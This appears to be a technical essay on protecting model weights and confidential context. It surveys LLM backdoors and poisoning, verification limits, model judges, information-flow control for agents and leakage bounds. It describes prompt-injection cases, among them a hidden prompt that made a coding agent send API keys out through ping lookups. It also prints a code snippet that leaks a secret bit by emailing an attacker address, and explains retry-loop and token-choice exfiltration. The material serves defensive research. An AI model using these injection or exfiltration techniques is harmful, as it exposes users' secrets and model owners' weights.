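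The second theorem shows that a backdoor can be hidden completely, but only in a much narrower class of models. It assumes that certain problems about lattices, which are regular grids of points in many dimensions, are hard to solve. These models have one hidden layer of random numbers, and training adjusts only the layer after it. The attacker runs the normal training algorithm on the normal data but replaces the random numbers with specially constructed ones that look random. No efficient test can then detect the backdoor, even with access to all the weights and training data.

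This second theorem doesn't cover language models, because training normally adjusts all their layers. *Injecting Undetectable Backdoors in Obfuscated Neural Networks and Language Models* (2024) extends the idea to them under a stronger cryptographic assumption. The trainer must also obfuscate the finished model, which means rewriting it so that nobody can work out how it operates, and this isn't a normal step in training a language model. The theorems show that no general method of inspection can be guaranteed to find every backdoor, but they don't show that any deployed model has one.

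Poisoning may give an attacker less power. *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* (Kaneko, 2026) considers an attacker who can influence training only through examples labelled as triggers or non-triggers. If the model acquires the trigger rule, it must have learned it from those examples, so a defender with equally many labelled examples could learn it by running the same procedure. The attacker therefore can't install a rule that is too hard for the defender to learn. In experiments on four language models with 7 to 9 billion parameters, the attack and the defender's reconstruction of the rule both succeeded when the rule was easy, and neither did better than chance when it was cryptographically hard.

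This result helps a defender only once they have examples of the trigger, which may not be until after an attack. Kaneko also points out that it is about reconstructing the trigger rule, not detecting that a model has a backdoor. It also doesn't seem to apply to the strongest attack in Hu and colleagues' experiments, where the poisoned documents described the rule in ordinary prose instead of demonstrating it. For the 4-billion-parameter model and the file-path trigger, the attack succeeded on 92.7% of prompts with these descriptions and 3.2% with example conversations.

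### Proving something about every input

Formal verification would replace tests with a proof. Vorobyov and Ilyushin (2026), in *Scaling Neural Network Verification with Tensor Parallelism and Fully Sharded Data Parallelism*, define the problem as showing that

ψ(f(x)) holds for every x in X,

where f is the network, X is a set of inputs and ψ is a property of the output. The most widely studied property is local robustness. For an image classifier, this means that every image within a small distance of a given one gets the same label. Even this is NP-complete for networks built from ReLU units, which pass on positive numbers and replace negative ones with zero. Verifiers that always reach an answer can therefore take exponential time in the worst case.

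An annual competition gives an idea of the sizes that researchers attempt. These are some of the networks that Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues (2026) list in *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)*:

| Network's task | Parameters |
|---|---|
| image classification (the largest network) | 138 million |
| image classification with small transformers | 68,000 to 76,000 |
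| aircraft collision detection | 13,000 |
| sentence classification | 4,000 |

These networks are from the competition's problems, which a tool may fail to solve within the time limit. Vorobyov and Ilyushin report a complete proof for one image classifier from a benchmark whose networks have at most 3.8 million parameters.

Transformers, the architecture behind most language models, are particularly difficult to verify. The competition's transformers were deliberately limited to two or three layers, and the property concerns only changes of up to 1/255 in each pixel's brightness. *Certified Mechanistic Interpretability* (2026) works with language models about the size of GPT-2, which dates from 2019, but its certificates also cover only bounded sets of inputs around chosen examples. An attacker can send a prompt unlike any example the owner has checked.

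*BEAVER* (2025), which presents a language model verifier, states that sound verification of these models is "generally considered infeasible" because of their size. Its own, narrower method expands possible answers token by token and checks each completed answer. *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models* (2026) also has a narrower aim, to prove limits on the probability of a harmful output. Expanding the answers to one prompt doesn't show how the model will respond to a different prompt that contains a trigger.

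Even with unlimited computing power, the owner would have to write down ψ. *Verification of Neural Networks (Lecture Notes)* (2026) argues that anyone who could specify correctness precisely would probably not need a neural network. An owner could require that no output contain the system prompt word for word, but a paraphrase or translation would satisfy this property and still reveal the secret. Specifying how much an output may reveal about the weights is even harder.

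### Training records

The owner could instead justify the endorsement by showing where the weights came from. If only trusted people supplied the data, the code and the random numbers, w would be trusted under the ordinary labelling rules without an endorsement. This might be realistic for a small model that a company trains on its own documents, but not for one trained on the public web.

Cryptographic proofs of training can show that a trainer ran the agreed algorithm on the agreed data. But the attack in Goldwasser and colleagues' second theorem uses the agreed algorithm and data and changes only the random numbers, so the client must also make sure that those are genuine. The client could supply them, the trainer could prove that it sampled them correctly, or several servers, at least one of them honest, could generate them together. Goldwasser and colleagues say that producing a proof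 of training takes considerably more work than the training itself. They also consider the approach much harder to use when the client relies on the trainer's expertise as well as its computers.

A proof of training doesn't show that the data is harmless. If the agreed data contains 250 poisoned documents, an honest trainer will install a backdoor and can then prove that they followed the instructions.

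Records of where each document came from help the owner exclude suspicious sources, or find the poisoned documents after an attack. But reputable sources can also contain poisoned text. Souly and colleagues cite an estimate that an attacker could manipulate up to 6.5% of the tokens in Wikipedia. Filtering is difficult too. Hu and colleagues argue that a filter would have to catch nearly every poisoned document, and some of the poisoned documents in their study were realistic technical notes with no unusual formatting.

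An owner can use tests, verification and records to reduce the risk, but for a large model trained on web text, these measures don't justify endorsing the weights for every possible prompt. Even a model with trusted weights could release information it shouldn't. For example, a model that a company had trained entirely on its own documents could still recite its system prompt.

### Language models that approve releases

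The main argument for using a model as a judge is that it can take meaning into account. Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) point out in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* that whether a personal assistant should disclose something depends on who is asking, why, and how they are related to the person concerned. A fixed rule can block anything that looks like a credit card number, but it would probably miss that "she'll be back at work once the chemotherapy ends" reveals a diagnosis, which a language model can easily recognise.

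The simplest arrangement is to have the agent's own model make the decision. Shim and colleagues tested an elaborate version in which the system prompt tells the agent to check the sender's identity and wait for the data owner's consent. Only 1.9% to 3.0% of private items leaked under the attacks that earlier researchers had used to develop this defence. When attackers disguised or divided their requests so that the model didn't recognise a disclosure, 43.8% to 75.6% leaked. Shim and colleagues attribute this to the model having to decide whether the rules apply while reading text the attacker controls.

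Their own system, FlowSeal, leaves the decision to a separate language model call, which a program outside the agent makes whenever a release needs a judgement about meaning. The judging model receives the protected records and the proposed output but not the conversation with the attacker. Across their tests, 0% to 3.3% of private items leaked, and the agent completed 72.4% of legitimate tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best alternative.

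These figures are for the whole system, which also uses labels and fixed checks, so they don't measure how often the judge alone is wrong. Shim and colleagues also exclude prompt injection from the attacks they consider. If an attacker could get the agent to include an instruction in the proposed output, it would reach the judge.

*GIF* (Štorek, Holzer and colleagues, 2026) reduces the amount of text the judge has to consider. It slightly changes the numbers that represent part of a prompt inside the model, then measures how much the probabilities of the next token change. In one example, a job applicant's CV contains an instruction for a hiring agent to recommend the applicant at a salary of $200,000. The paper estimates that 82 bits of information flow from this instruction into the agent's recommendation, compared with 27 bits from the employer's criteria.

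A small language model then judges only the parts with a strong influence. Štorek and colleagues found that, with this help, a model with 8 billion parameters matched or beat GPT-5.5 working alone, at less than one-eightieth of the cost. They scored the models with F1, which combines missed violations and false alarms. Their machine-checked proof that the method doesn't underestimate influence covers only very small changes around a single prompt, and they state that it doesn't verify any deployed model.

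Under the typing rule, a judge's verdict v is untrusted if the attacker may have influenced x, even if the judge's weights are trustworthy, because the judge has to read x to decide whether it is safe to release. A judge that read only trusted data could give a trusted verdict, but it couldn't check what the attacker had got the agent to write. The server could endorse the attacker's messages when they arrive, as it does with prompts, but the weaker condition would then not cover anything the attacker achieved through those messages, including fooling the judge.

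Low error rates also give limited protection against an attacker who can keep trying. If each attempt had an independent 0.5% chance of getting past the judge, 200 attempts would give the attacker a 63% chance of succeeding at least once. Real attempts aren't independent, and an attacker who learns from each refusal may need fewer.

For reasons like these, *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* recommends designing systems without assuming that the model resists manipulation or is free of backdoors. A more robust model can help other defences, but security shouldn't depend on it alone. A judge can still be useful as an additional check if it can only block releases that other rules allow. Its mistakes then can't authorise anything those rules forbid, although a refusal may reveal a little about the secret.

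Judges are also better suited to protecting secrets in the context than secrets in the weights. A judge can compare a proposed answer with a confidential document because both are text, but it has no such text to compare when the secret is w. A judge that reads answers one at a time also won't detect distillation.

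## Leaving the release decision to a small program outside the model

An owner who can't verify a model can leave it out of the release decision. Every output must instead pass through a release gate, a small trusted program outside the model. The gate compares the labels on each proposed message or action with a fixed policy, then allows or blocks it. The security argument doesn't depend on the model's behaviour, so it holds for any model, even one that an attacker has trained. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* compares this to an operating system, which has to handle any request a hostile program might make.

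A gate can't protect data that can get around it. The same paper describes an attack on Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. The attack used a prompt hidden in a code file to make the agent read API keys and send them out with `ping`, a command that checks whether another computer is reachable. Claude Code asked for human approval before running many commands that could send data to unknown domains, but it ran `ping` without asking. `ping` looks up a computer's address before contacting it, and this lookup carried the keys to the attacker's server.

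### How labels follow a conversation

In the LLMbda calculus, the language for agents from Garby and colleagues, a program manages its conversation with the model through four commands:

- `send` adds a message and raises the conversation's label to cover the message's label.
- `recv` samples the model's response, parses it as data or code, and runs it with pc set to the conversation's label.
- `fork` runs part of the program on a temporary copy of the conversation, then restores the original.
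- `clear` empties the conversation.

The gate doesn't depend on the model being honest, because the rule for `recv` ensures that any code the model writes after reading a stranger's email can produce only untrusted results.

An agent that kept everything in one conversation would soon lose access to most of its tools. A program can avoid this by forking the conversation, clearing the copy and asking about the email there. The answer is untrusted, but the main conversation stays trusted because it never contained the email. This is a version of the dual-LLM pattern, in which one model plans and calls tools while another reads untrusted data but can't call tools.

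The tools check labels before they act. In one of Garby and colleagues' examples, a user asks an agent to send a meeting reminder, but an email in the inbox contains an instruction to send a cancellation instead. An agent that read the email in its main conversation sent the cancellation. A second agent wrote its plan before reading the email and took only the recipient's address from it. Its `send_email` tool accepted only a trusted subject and body, and the agent sent the reminder. The email's text can't change the subject or body of any message that passes this check, but it can still change the recipient.

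### What the two theorems guarantee

The main theorem is noninterference for programs that make random choices and may not finish. It compares two runs that differ only in data the observer can't see. If both runs always finish, the observer must see each possible result with the same probability in both. Otherwise, the theorem allows a small difference. Suppose a program that has access to a secret bank balance produces these results:

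| Result | Balance is low | Balance is high | Larger of the two |
|---|---|---|---|
| "yes" | 60% | 50% | 60% |
| "no" | 30% | 40% | 40% |
| does not finish | 10% | 10% | |

The theorem allows this because the larger of the two probabilities for "yes" and the larger of the two for "no" add up to at most 100%. The two runs could be the same program with different answers cut off before they appeared. If the low balance gave "yes" 70% of the time and "no" 20%, the total would be 110%, which the theorem rules out. The observed distributions can therefore differ by at most the average probability of not finishing, which is 10% here. A program that the gate stops also counts as unfinished.

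The second theorem, the insulated version, covers programs that endorse data. Endorsement deliberately weakens the guarantee about trust, so the theorem is about an observer who can see all public data, trusted or not. If two runs have the same public inputs and differ only in their secrets, this observer can't tell them apart, except by whether they finish. This holds for any untrusted inputs the attacker chooses and any endorsements in the program.

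However, the insulated theorem isn't about robust release. Robustness compares what different attacks reveal when a program intentionally releases something. Under this theorem, no attack reveals anything, so the program is trivially robust because it has no release for an attacker to influence. Garby and colleagues point out that swapping the two dimensions of the label would turn endorsement into declassification. But the theorem would then protect only integrity, and wouldn't cover how an attacker might influence the declassified secrets.

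### Two leaks in CaMeL

CaMeL also uses the dual-LLM pattern. Its planning model turns the user's request into a program in a restricted form of Python, and an interpreter runs it while tracking where each value came from and who may receive it. The two leaks that Garby and colleagues found, through a skipped assignment and the retry loop, both evade this tracking.

Suppose an attacker wants to know whether a customer's balance is above some threshold. CaMeL blocks a program that sends an email directly from inside `if balance > threshold`. A less direct program works:

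```
tmp := true; rich := true
if balance > threshold then tmp := false
if tmp then rich := false
if rich then send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, the second line makes `tmp` false and secret. The third line then skips its assignment, so `rich` stays true and public, and the email goes out. If the balance is below the threshold, `tmp` stays true and public, and the third line makes `rich` false without making it secret. In both cases, `rich` is public and reveals whether the balance is above the threshold.

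LLMbda programs can't reassign variables, but they could try to leak a secret by adding a message to the conversation only if the secret is true. The interpreter stops any program that tries to send a message to a public conversation from inside a branch that depends on a secret. An observer who notices that the program stopped can still learn one bit.

CaMeL's untracked retry loop lets an attacker collect many such bits. The attacker can arrange for the policy to block the first attempt if the first bit of a secret is 1, the second attempt if the second bit is 1, and so on. The loop records which attempts failed but starts each new one as though it held no secret information. A 64-bit secret takes 64 attempts. CaMeL censors the error messages that pass between attempts, but Garby and colleagues say this gives no formal guarantee.

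Their own agent, Randori, retries inside LLMbda. It first tests its code on made-up data, where reading a file returns a fixed placeholder and sending money does nothing. Failures in these tests reveal nothing about the real account, so the model can correct its code freely before writing the version that runs on real data.

*SPA* doesn't retry. Its planner writes one complete plan for each request and gets no feedback on whether the checker rejected it. The checker examines the whole plan before any tool runs, so it can also account for assignments on branches that won't be taken. *SPA* writes plans in a restricted language to make this possible. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) recommends a similar change for CaMeL because Python features such as exceptions and dynamic typing make information flow hard to analyse.

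### The banking tests

Garby and colleagues tested Randori on AgentDojo's banking suite, which has 16 tasks and nine attacks. They ran each task with each attack three times on each of three models, for 1,296 attacked runs. They also ran CaMeL with two of the models, with its policy checks on and off, but some of the attacked CaMeL runs didn't complete.

| Agent | Model | Tasks completed without an attack | Successful attacks |
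|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 | 2 of 432 |
| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 36 of 48 | 0 of 432 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 | 0 of 432 |
| Randori without endorsement | Qwen3.7-plus | 30 of 48 | 0 of 432 |
| Randori without endorsement | MiMo-v2.5 | 26 of 48 | 0 of 432 |
| CaMeL, checks off | GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL, checks off | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 | 4 of 382 |
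| CaMeL, checks on | GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 231 |
| CaMeL, checks on | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 357 |

In both successful attacks on Randori, the user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file with a different payment request. The agent's plan endorsed the file's contents, so the transfer passed the check. Without endorsement, the gate blocks this attack, but it also blocks legitimate payment requests in files.

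Planning, rather than labels, stopped most of the attacks. In 97 of the 144 combinations, the attack needed a tool call or file that would never appear in a plan for the user's task. An agent that writes its plan before reading untrusted data generally resists these attacks without any labels. The remaining 47 combinations, which account for 423 of Randori's runs, are a better test of the gate. The attacks come with the benchmark, so they don't show how Randori would fare against an attacker who had studied it.

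Randori completed about twice as many tasks as CaMeL did with its checks on, but the comparison is uneven because Garby and colleagues gave Randori's tools somewhat looser policies than CaMeL's and let the model add endorsements to its own plans. The 95% confidence intervals are also wide, at about 19 to 27 percentage points either side, because there were only 16 tasks.

When the model can write endorsements, the gate no longer makes the whole decision. Garby and colleagues acknowledge that nothing prevents an overly permissive planner from endorsing whatever it likes. Without endorsements, even a plan from a fully compromised model has to obey the tools' policies. If the model can endorse, the secrets are still safe under the insulated theorem, but an attacker may be able to choose who receives the money.

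### Restricting endorsement

The calculus already prevents an endorsed value from being more trusted than pc, so code that runs because of untrusted data can't make anything trusted. But if a program mistakenly endorses the attacker's data and a model then writes code based on it, that code runs with a trusted pc and can make further endorsements.

Garby and colleagues' appendix describes an optional wrapper, robust endorsement, that blocks such chains. It marks every value it endorses, and the mark passes to anything computed from that value. The wrapper won't endorse a value that is already marked. Programs, including code written by the model, can use only the wrapper and not the original command.

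The researchers don't have a formal definition of what this achieves. A definition based on final results can't distinguish two programs that produce the same results with the same labels, even when the attacker controls whether an endorsement happens in one but not the other. They also doubt that a definition based on attacker knowledge would work for programs that make random choices. For example, publishing an encrypted message reveals nothing at the time, but publishing the key later lets the attacker read it.

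A second wrapper endorses only values from a short fixed list. For example, an agent might have a separate model sort incoming emails into categories and use the category as the subject of its reply:

```
w := endorse(v)
if w is "invoice", "complaint" or "general" then return w

else return v
```

If v isn't on the list, the wrapper returns the original, which is still untrusted. The wrapper has to endorse before it tests, because testing the untrusted v would make pc untrusted, and the endorsement would then have no effect.

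A choice among n categories carries at most log₂(n) bits, so eight categories allow the attacker at most 3 bits per email. An agent that sorts 100 emails could therefore pass on 300 bits of the attacker's choosing. Garby and colleagues haven't formally proved this limit for their wrapper, and it wouldn't help in their banking tests, where the agent endorses account numbers and amounts that can't be chosen from a short list.

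### Where other systems allow a release

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, an agent that checks labels before each tool call. It has two basic policies. The confidentiality policy lets a tool send information only to people who are allowed to read it. The integrity policy allows a call with real consequences, such as sending an email, only if the decision to make the call and all the call's arguments are trusted.

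Costa and colleagues observe that using the integrity policy alone gives "a form of robust declassification". A secret can reach someone who wasn't allowed to read it only if no untrusted data has affected the call, in which case the user presumably intended the release. The policy closely matches the 2006 typing rule, with the decision in place of pc and the arguments in place of the declassified value.

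However, the policies in their AgentDojo tests didn't check the arguments. Zdancewic's early type system had a similar gap, since it checked whether a release happened but not which value the program released. In one of Costa and colleagues' examples, the user asks for a summary of some emails. A malicious email can't change where FIDES sends the summary, but it can make the summary empty.

FIDES also has a weaker confidentiality guarantee than LLMbda, called explicit secrecy, which covers the direct copying of secrets but not what an observer can infer from the agent's choice of tools. Costa and colleagues consider noninterference too restrictive, because an agent that had read anything secret could no longer use any tool with public effects. FIDES can make an exception for answers from a small set, such as whether an email contains a meeting request, but Costa and colleagues didn't use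 this option in their tests.

With the policies on, they count no successful attacks on FIDES, after discounting three that AgentDojo scored as successes. Using GPT-4o, FIDES completed 52.5% of the banking tasks, compared with 98.8% for an agent with no defences. Task completion also fell in *SPA*. Turning on its label checks reduced successful attacks to zero under AgentDojo's tool-knowledge attack, but lowered task completion without attacks from 53% to 29%, mainly because many legitimate tasks require acting on outside information.

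Some newer systems allow individual exceptions:

- *Agent libOS* can require a person to approve a single-use release. Approval covers secrecy only, so the release still fails if the data is less trusted than the action requires.
- *APPA* (2026) allows an exception for one exact tool call. A fixed rule, a person or a language model can approve it, and the approval doesn't carry over to later calls.
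- *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (2026) lets a model propose a value but leaves the release to trusted code. The code puts the value into a standard form, checks it against the policy and releases it for one particular field. It may release a time interval or a file path, for instance, but the model's free-text explanations remain untrusted.

*APPA* guarantees that every exception has an approval on record, but not that the approval was justified. If the approver is a model that has to read the attacker's text, its verdict is untrusted, like that of any other model judge. Free text is the main product of a language model API, so a rule that releases only short typed values would suit an agent's tools better than a chat service.

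### Why these theorems don't cover the weights

FIDES's labels, like LLMbda's, cover only the data that the agent handles, not the model's weights. In Costa and colleagues' threat model, the model is trusted and public, so its weights aren't secret.

Garby and colleagues' theorems hold even for a hostile model, but they compare runs that use the same model. To learn whether a program leaks the model's weights, we would have to compare runs that use different models.

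Even the simplest program would fail this comparison. Suppose an agent asks the model who wrote *Middlemarch*. The question is public and trusted, so LLMbda labels the response public and trusted too and allows the agent to publish it, even though the answer reveals something about the model's weights.

An owner could make the labels reflect the secret by adding a second confidentiality label for the weights. If the program begins each conversation with an empty message that has this label, every later response will have it too. The gate then removes only the weights label, so a response based on another customer's contract would still have the contract's label and couldn't go to the wrong person.

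The insulated theorem applies to any two independent dimensions of a label, so one could be secrecy of the weights and the other secrecy of the context. Removing the weights label would then leave the guarantee for the context intact, though the theorem would still prove nothing about the weights. Garby and colleagues don't discuss this case, but it follows from the theorem's general form.

### A release gate for the weights

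A gate for the weights would treat everything the model produces as secret, including its text, its scores and the time it takes. For each request, it would release exactly 500 tokens, for example, and nothing else:

```
n := 500                # public, trusted
t := endorse(u)         # public, trusted
y := M(w, t)            # secret
p := format(y, n)       # secret
send(declassify(p))     # at a fixed time after the request
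```

The function `format` keeps the first n tokens of the answer and discards the scores. If the answer is too short or contains something that isn't a valid token, `format` fills the gap with blanks. The owner sets n and the delay in advance, and requests have no fields for changing them. With n set to 500, a customer who asks for a short answer still receives 500 tokens, most of them blank.

The response is always 500 tokens long and arrives after the same delay, whatever the prompt and the weights. Its length and timing therefore satisfy noninterference and are robust. The attacker can still influence its content, which isn't robust because different prompts reveal different facts about the weights.

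The 2006 typing rule has separate requirements for the decision to release and the value released. It requires pc to be trusted, which holds here even if an attacker has poisoned the weights, because the gate releases something after every request without looking at y. The rule also requires the released value to be trusted, which fails if the weights are untrusted. A gate that read y and sometimes withheld it would fail the first requirement too, because y would then affect whether the release happened.

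The customer still chooses when to send a request. A stricter server could send each customer a response at fixed times and fill it with blanks if no prompt had arrived, though much of what it sent would be blank.

This gate would block the 2024 attacks on OpenAI's final layer in their original form, since those used log-probabilities and logit bias. The fixed delay would also hide the response times that Ellis and colleagues used to estimate the number of layers. But the delay has to be long enough for the slowest answer, so customers would wait that long for every answer and couldn't read it as the model wrote it.

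The gate doesn't make the text any less useful to someone training a copy of the model. It also can't detect a message hidden in the choice of tokens, because any sequence of 500 valid tokens has the right format. With a vocabulary of 32,000, each token can carry about 15 bits, so a response of 500 tokens can carry about 7,500 bits. An attacker who had tampered with the server could use those bits to send out part of w in every response. Preventing this would require a limit on the total leakage or a check that the server had computed the tokens correctly.

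## Limits on leakage that hold for every choice of prompts

If a model's owner can't stop a tampered server from hiding parts of the weights in its answers, they can at least limit the total amount that leaks.

Robustness requires that an active attacker learns no more than a passive one. A natural way to relax this is to let the active attacker learn a limited amount more. At an API, a passive attacker sends no prompts and learns nothing, so the extra amount is everything the attacker learns. The owner therefore needs a leakage bound, a number B fixed in advance such that

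for every strategy σ, leakage(σ) ≤ B.

A strategy σ is a rule for choosing each prompt based on the answers so far. The owner sets B before the attacker chooses σ, so B has to cover strategies that nobody has thought of yet.

A robust program can still leak everything, like the server that publishes all its weights without being asked. Conversely, a server that answers one yes-or-no question of the customer's choice and then shuts down isn't robust, but it leaks at most one bit.

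In *Quantitative Robust Declassification*, Zhu, Zhuang and Chen (2014) use Shannon's information theory to define a robustness rate, and show that a rate of 1 is equivalent to robust declassification. They calculated the rate for a laundering attack on a program that releases an average salary, and their experiments agreed with the calculation. But the server that publishes its weights without being asked would also have a rate of 1, so the rate can't replace B.

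Clarkson and Schneider's *Quantification of Integrity* measures contamination, the amount of untrusted information that reaches trusted outputs. Contamination is the integrity counterpart of leakage. Low contamination would not be a sensible goal for an API, because customers want answers that depend on their prompts.

### The attacker's best guess

To set B, the owner needs a way to measure leakage. Smith (2009), in *On the Foundations of Quantitative Information Flow*, starts from the chance that an attacker guesses the secret correctly in one try. Before the attacker sees anything, this chance is the probability of the most likely secret, which Smith calls the vulnerability, V(s). Afterwards it is V(s | answers), the average probability that the attacker's best guess is right. Min-entropy leakage is

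leakage = log₂( V(s | answers) / V(s) ).

Each bit of leakage doubles the attacker's chance of guessing the secret h. If h is a four-bit number and all 16 values are equally likely, that chance starts at 1/16. Learning whether h is below 8 raises it to 1/8, so one bit has leaked. Comparing h with four well-chosen thresholds raises it to 1, so four bits have leaked.

An attacker with m guesses succeeds with probability at most m times the vulnerability, which is the probability of success with a single guess. So if a realistic number of guesses gives the attacker a good chance, one guess already gives them a noticeable chance.

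Most earlier work measured leakage with Shannon entropy, which is roughly the average number of bits needed to communicate a value. Smith uses two programs to show why this can mislead. The table gives the results for a 64-bit secret h whose values are all equally likely.

| Program | Shannon leakage | Min-entropy leakage | Chance of guessing h afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
| `if h mod 8 = 0 then p := h else p := 1` | 8.2 bits | 61 bits | about 1 in 8 |
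| publish the last 9 bits of h | 9 bits | 9 bits | 1 in 2⁵⁵ |

The second program leaks slightly more by Shannon's measure. But the first publishes the entire secret an eighth of the time, while the second leaves the attacker with almost no chance of guessing it.

### Counting the possible answers

If an attacker receives q answers, each from a set of N possible ones, there are N^q possible sequences of answers. This number by itself limits the leakage.

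To see why, imagine an outsider who has never used the API. The outsider makes up a random sequence of q answers, follows the attacker's strategy as if these answers were real, and makes the guess that the attacker would have made. The made-up sequence matches the real one with probability 1/N^q. The outsider's chance of guessing the weights is therefore at least

V(w | answers) / N^q.

But someone who has seen no answers can't have a better chance than V(w). It follows that V(w | answers) is at most N^q times V(w), and taking logarithms gives the counting bound:

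leakage ≤ q × log₂(N).

The argument doesn't depend on how the attacker chose the prompts or how the server computed the answers. It also holds if the model samples its answers, and if the attacker has unlimited computing power. Choosing prompts based on earlier answers can help an attacker reach the limit sooner, but it doesn't increase the number of possible answer sequences.

The true leakage may be much lower. Smith proves that if a program always gives the same output for the same secret, and all values of the secret are equally likely, the leakage is exactly log₂ of the number of outputs that can occur. Four threshold questions can produce 16 sequences of answers, so they leak four bits. Four guesses at a password can produce only five outcomes, because either one of the guesses is right or none is, so they leak about 2.3 bits. Yet a single question of either kind leaks one bit. Smith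 considers this a drawback of the measure, since the leakage of one step doesn't determine the leakage of several.

### Attackers who adapt

Smith's basic model has a secret and an output but no attacker input, so applying it to an API means fixing a strategy and treating all the answers as one output. Köpf and Basin's *An information-theoretic model for adaptive side-channel attacks* includes the attacker's choices by representing an attack strategy as a list of adaptive decisions. Side-channel attacks infer a secret from physical measurements, such as how long a device takes to encrypt a message. The journal version expresses the attacker's remaining uncertainty as a function of the number of interactions. For an API, the counting bound implies that this uncertainty falls by at most log₂(N) bits per answer.

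Boreale and Pampaloni, in *Quantitative Information Flow under Generic Leakage Functions and Adaptive Adversaries*, define the maximum leakage over all strategies and compare attackers who adapt with attackers who don't. If the number of queries is unlimited, both kinds of attacker reach the same maximum. This maximum depends only on which secrets no query can tell apart. For an API, those secrets are sets of weights that give the same output for every prompt.

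They also prove that if there are n possible queries, an attacker who can't base queries on earlier answers needs at most n times as many as one who can. For a small database that accepts 20 different queries, adapting therefore reduces the number needed by at most a factor of 20. A language model accepts an astronomical number of prompts, so the bound doesn't rule out an enormous advantage from adapting.

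Boreale and Pampaloni show how to calculate an attacker's best strategy for a fixed number of queries by working backwards from the last one. The calculation requires tracking the probability of every possible secret after every possible series of answers, which isn't feasible when the secret is a large model's weights. The owner of an API therefore has to rely on the cruder counting bound.

### A thousand answers and a terabyte

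Suppose a model has a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens and the gate releases exactly 500 tokens per answer. Each token carries at most log₂(100,000) ≈ 16.6 bits. A thousand answers then carry at most

1,000 × 500 × 16.6 ≈ 8.3 million bits,

or about 1 megabyte. A model with a trillion one-byte weights takes up 1 terabyte, about a million times as much.

| Answers of 500 tokens | Most they can carry | Share of the weights file |
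|---|---|---|
| 1,000 | 1.04 MB | 0.0001% |
| 1 million | 1.04 GB | 0.1% |
| 16 million | 16.6 GB | 1.7% |
| 963 million | 1 TB | 100% |

These limits hold even if an attacker has replaced the server's code with a program that sends out the weights file piece by piece. They require only that the gate counts the tokens correctly and lets nothing else out.

"Nothing else" rules out every other signal a customer could observe. If the server returned a 32-bit log-probability with each token, an answer could carry almost three times as much. If customers could distinguish 1,000 different response times, each answer could carry another 10 bits.

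A limit per account doesn't limit an attacker with many accounts. If each account could get 1,000 answers a day, sending out a terabyte through one account would take more than 2,600 years. With 20,000 accounts, roughly the number that Anthropic says one reseller ran at once, it would take about seven weeks. The owner would have to set a combined limit for all accounts that might belong to the same attacker, which at a public API could be any of them. A popular service sends out a billion answers quickly, so a combined limit for all its customers would be either too high to protect the weights or too low for the service to operate.

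### What a count of bits leaves out

A leakage limit of 1 megabyte does not protect some valuable secrets, because they are much smaller than a weights file. OpenAI asked researchers not to publish the widths of two of its models, but a width below 65,536 takes only 16 bits, less than a single token can carry. A 64-bit password fits into four tokens, and a typical system prompt fits into one or two answers.

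The size of the file can also overstate how much the attacker has to learn. Suppose a company takes a public model and adds 500,000 one-byte weights of its own, or half a megabyte. A thousand answers could in principle reveal all of them. In a more extreme case, the attacker knows the training program and all the data, and lacks only the random number generator's 32-bit seed. Two tokens can carry 33 bits, which is enough to identify the weights, though the attacker might have to repeat the training billions of times to recover them from those bits.

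An attacker also doesn't need most of the weights to copy useful behaviour. If each answer had 500 tokens, the 16 million exchanges in Anthropic's allegations would have carried at most 1.7% of a terabyte file, but that percentage is a poor measure of their value for distillation.

Two programs that leak the same number of bits can pose different threats. Smith compares a program that publishes the secret h an eighth of the time with one that always publishes all but its last three bits. For a 64-bit secret, both leak about 61 bits. If the attacker can make several guesses, the second program is worse, because eight guesses are always enough. If a wrong guess sets off an alarm, the first may be worse, because the attacker knows when they have the whole secret and can wait until then to guess.

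### How approximate answers reveal a database

Operators of statistical databases have long had a similar problem. They want to answer questions about groups without revealing facts about individuals, but an analyst can sometimes work out those facts by combining answers. For example, someone who asks how many employees have diabetes, and then how many employees other than the finance director have it, learns whether the finance director does.

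*The Theory of Reconstruction Attacks* explains why making answers slightly wrong often fails to prevent leakage. It credits Dinur and Nissim with introducing reconstruction attacks in 2003. In their setting, each of n people has one secret bit, such as whether they have diabetes. The attacker names any group and receives the number of ones in it, with an error of at most E.

Suppose the attacker asks about every possible group, then searches for any list of n bits consistent with all the answers. Consider the group of people whose bit is really 0 but is 1 in the attacker's list. The true count for this group is zero, and the count from the attacker's list is the size of the group. The server's answer is within E of both counts, so the group contains at most 2E people. The same argument applies to people whose bit is really 1 but is 0 in the list, so the attacker is wrong about at most 4E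 people in total. With 10,000 people and errors of up to 100, the attacker gets at least 96% of the bits right.

Nobody could ask about every group that can be formed from 10,000 people, but Dinur and Nissim also gave an efficient attack. It shows that errors in answers about n people must be at least of the order of √n to protect them from attackers with realistic computing power. *The Theory of Reconstruction Attacks* quotes a general version of this result from a textbook by Dwork and Roth: "overly accurate answers to too many questions will inevitably destroy privacy".

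### Differential privacy

Reconstruction attacks led directly to the definition of differential privacy, a limit on how much one person's record can affect what comes out. A randomised procedure A is ε-differentially private if, for any two datasets D and D′ that differ in one record, and for every set S of possible outputs,

Pr[A(D) ∈ S] ≤ e^ε × Pr[A(D′) ∈ S].

With ε = 0.1, including someone's record makes any outcome at most about 10.5% more likely. A server can achieve this for a question like "how many people have diabetes?" by adding random noise with an average size of about 10 people.

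When an analyst asks a series of questions, the output is the whole series of answers, and the inequality has to hold for every strategy of choosing the questions. Like a leakage bound, it allows the attacker to influence the output but limits what the attacker can achieve by doing so. The guarantee also composes, so k answers that are each ε-differentially private are together kε-differentially private, even if the analyst chose each question after seeing the earlier answers. This is because each answer changes the ratio of the two probabilities by a factor of at most e^ε, and these factors multiply. A hundred answers with ε = 0.1 give a total ε of 10, which allows the ratio to change by a factor of about 22,000. The server therefore has to stop answering eventually or add more noise to each answer.

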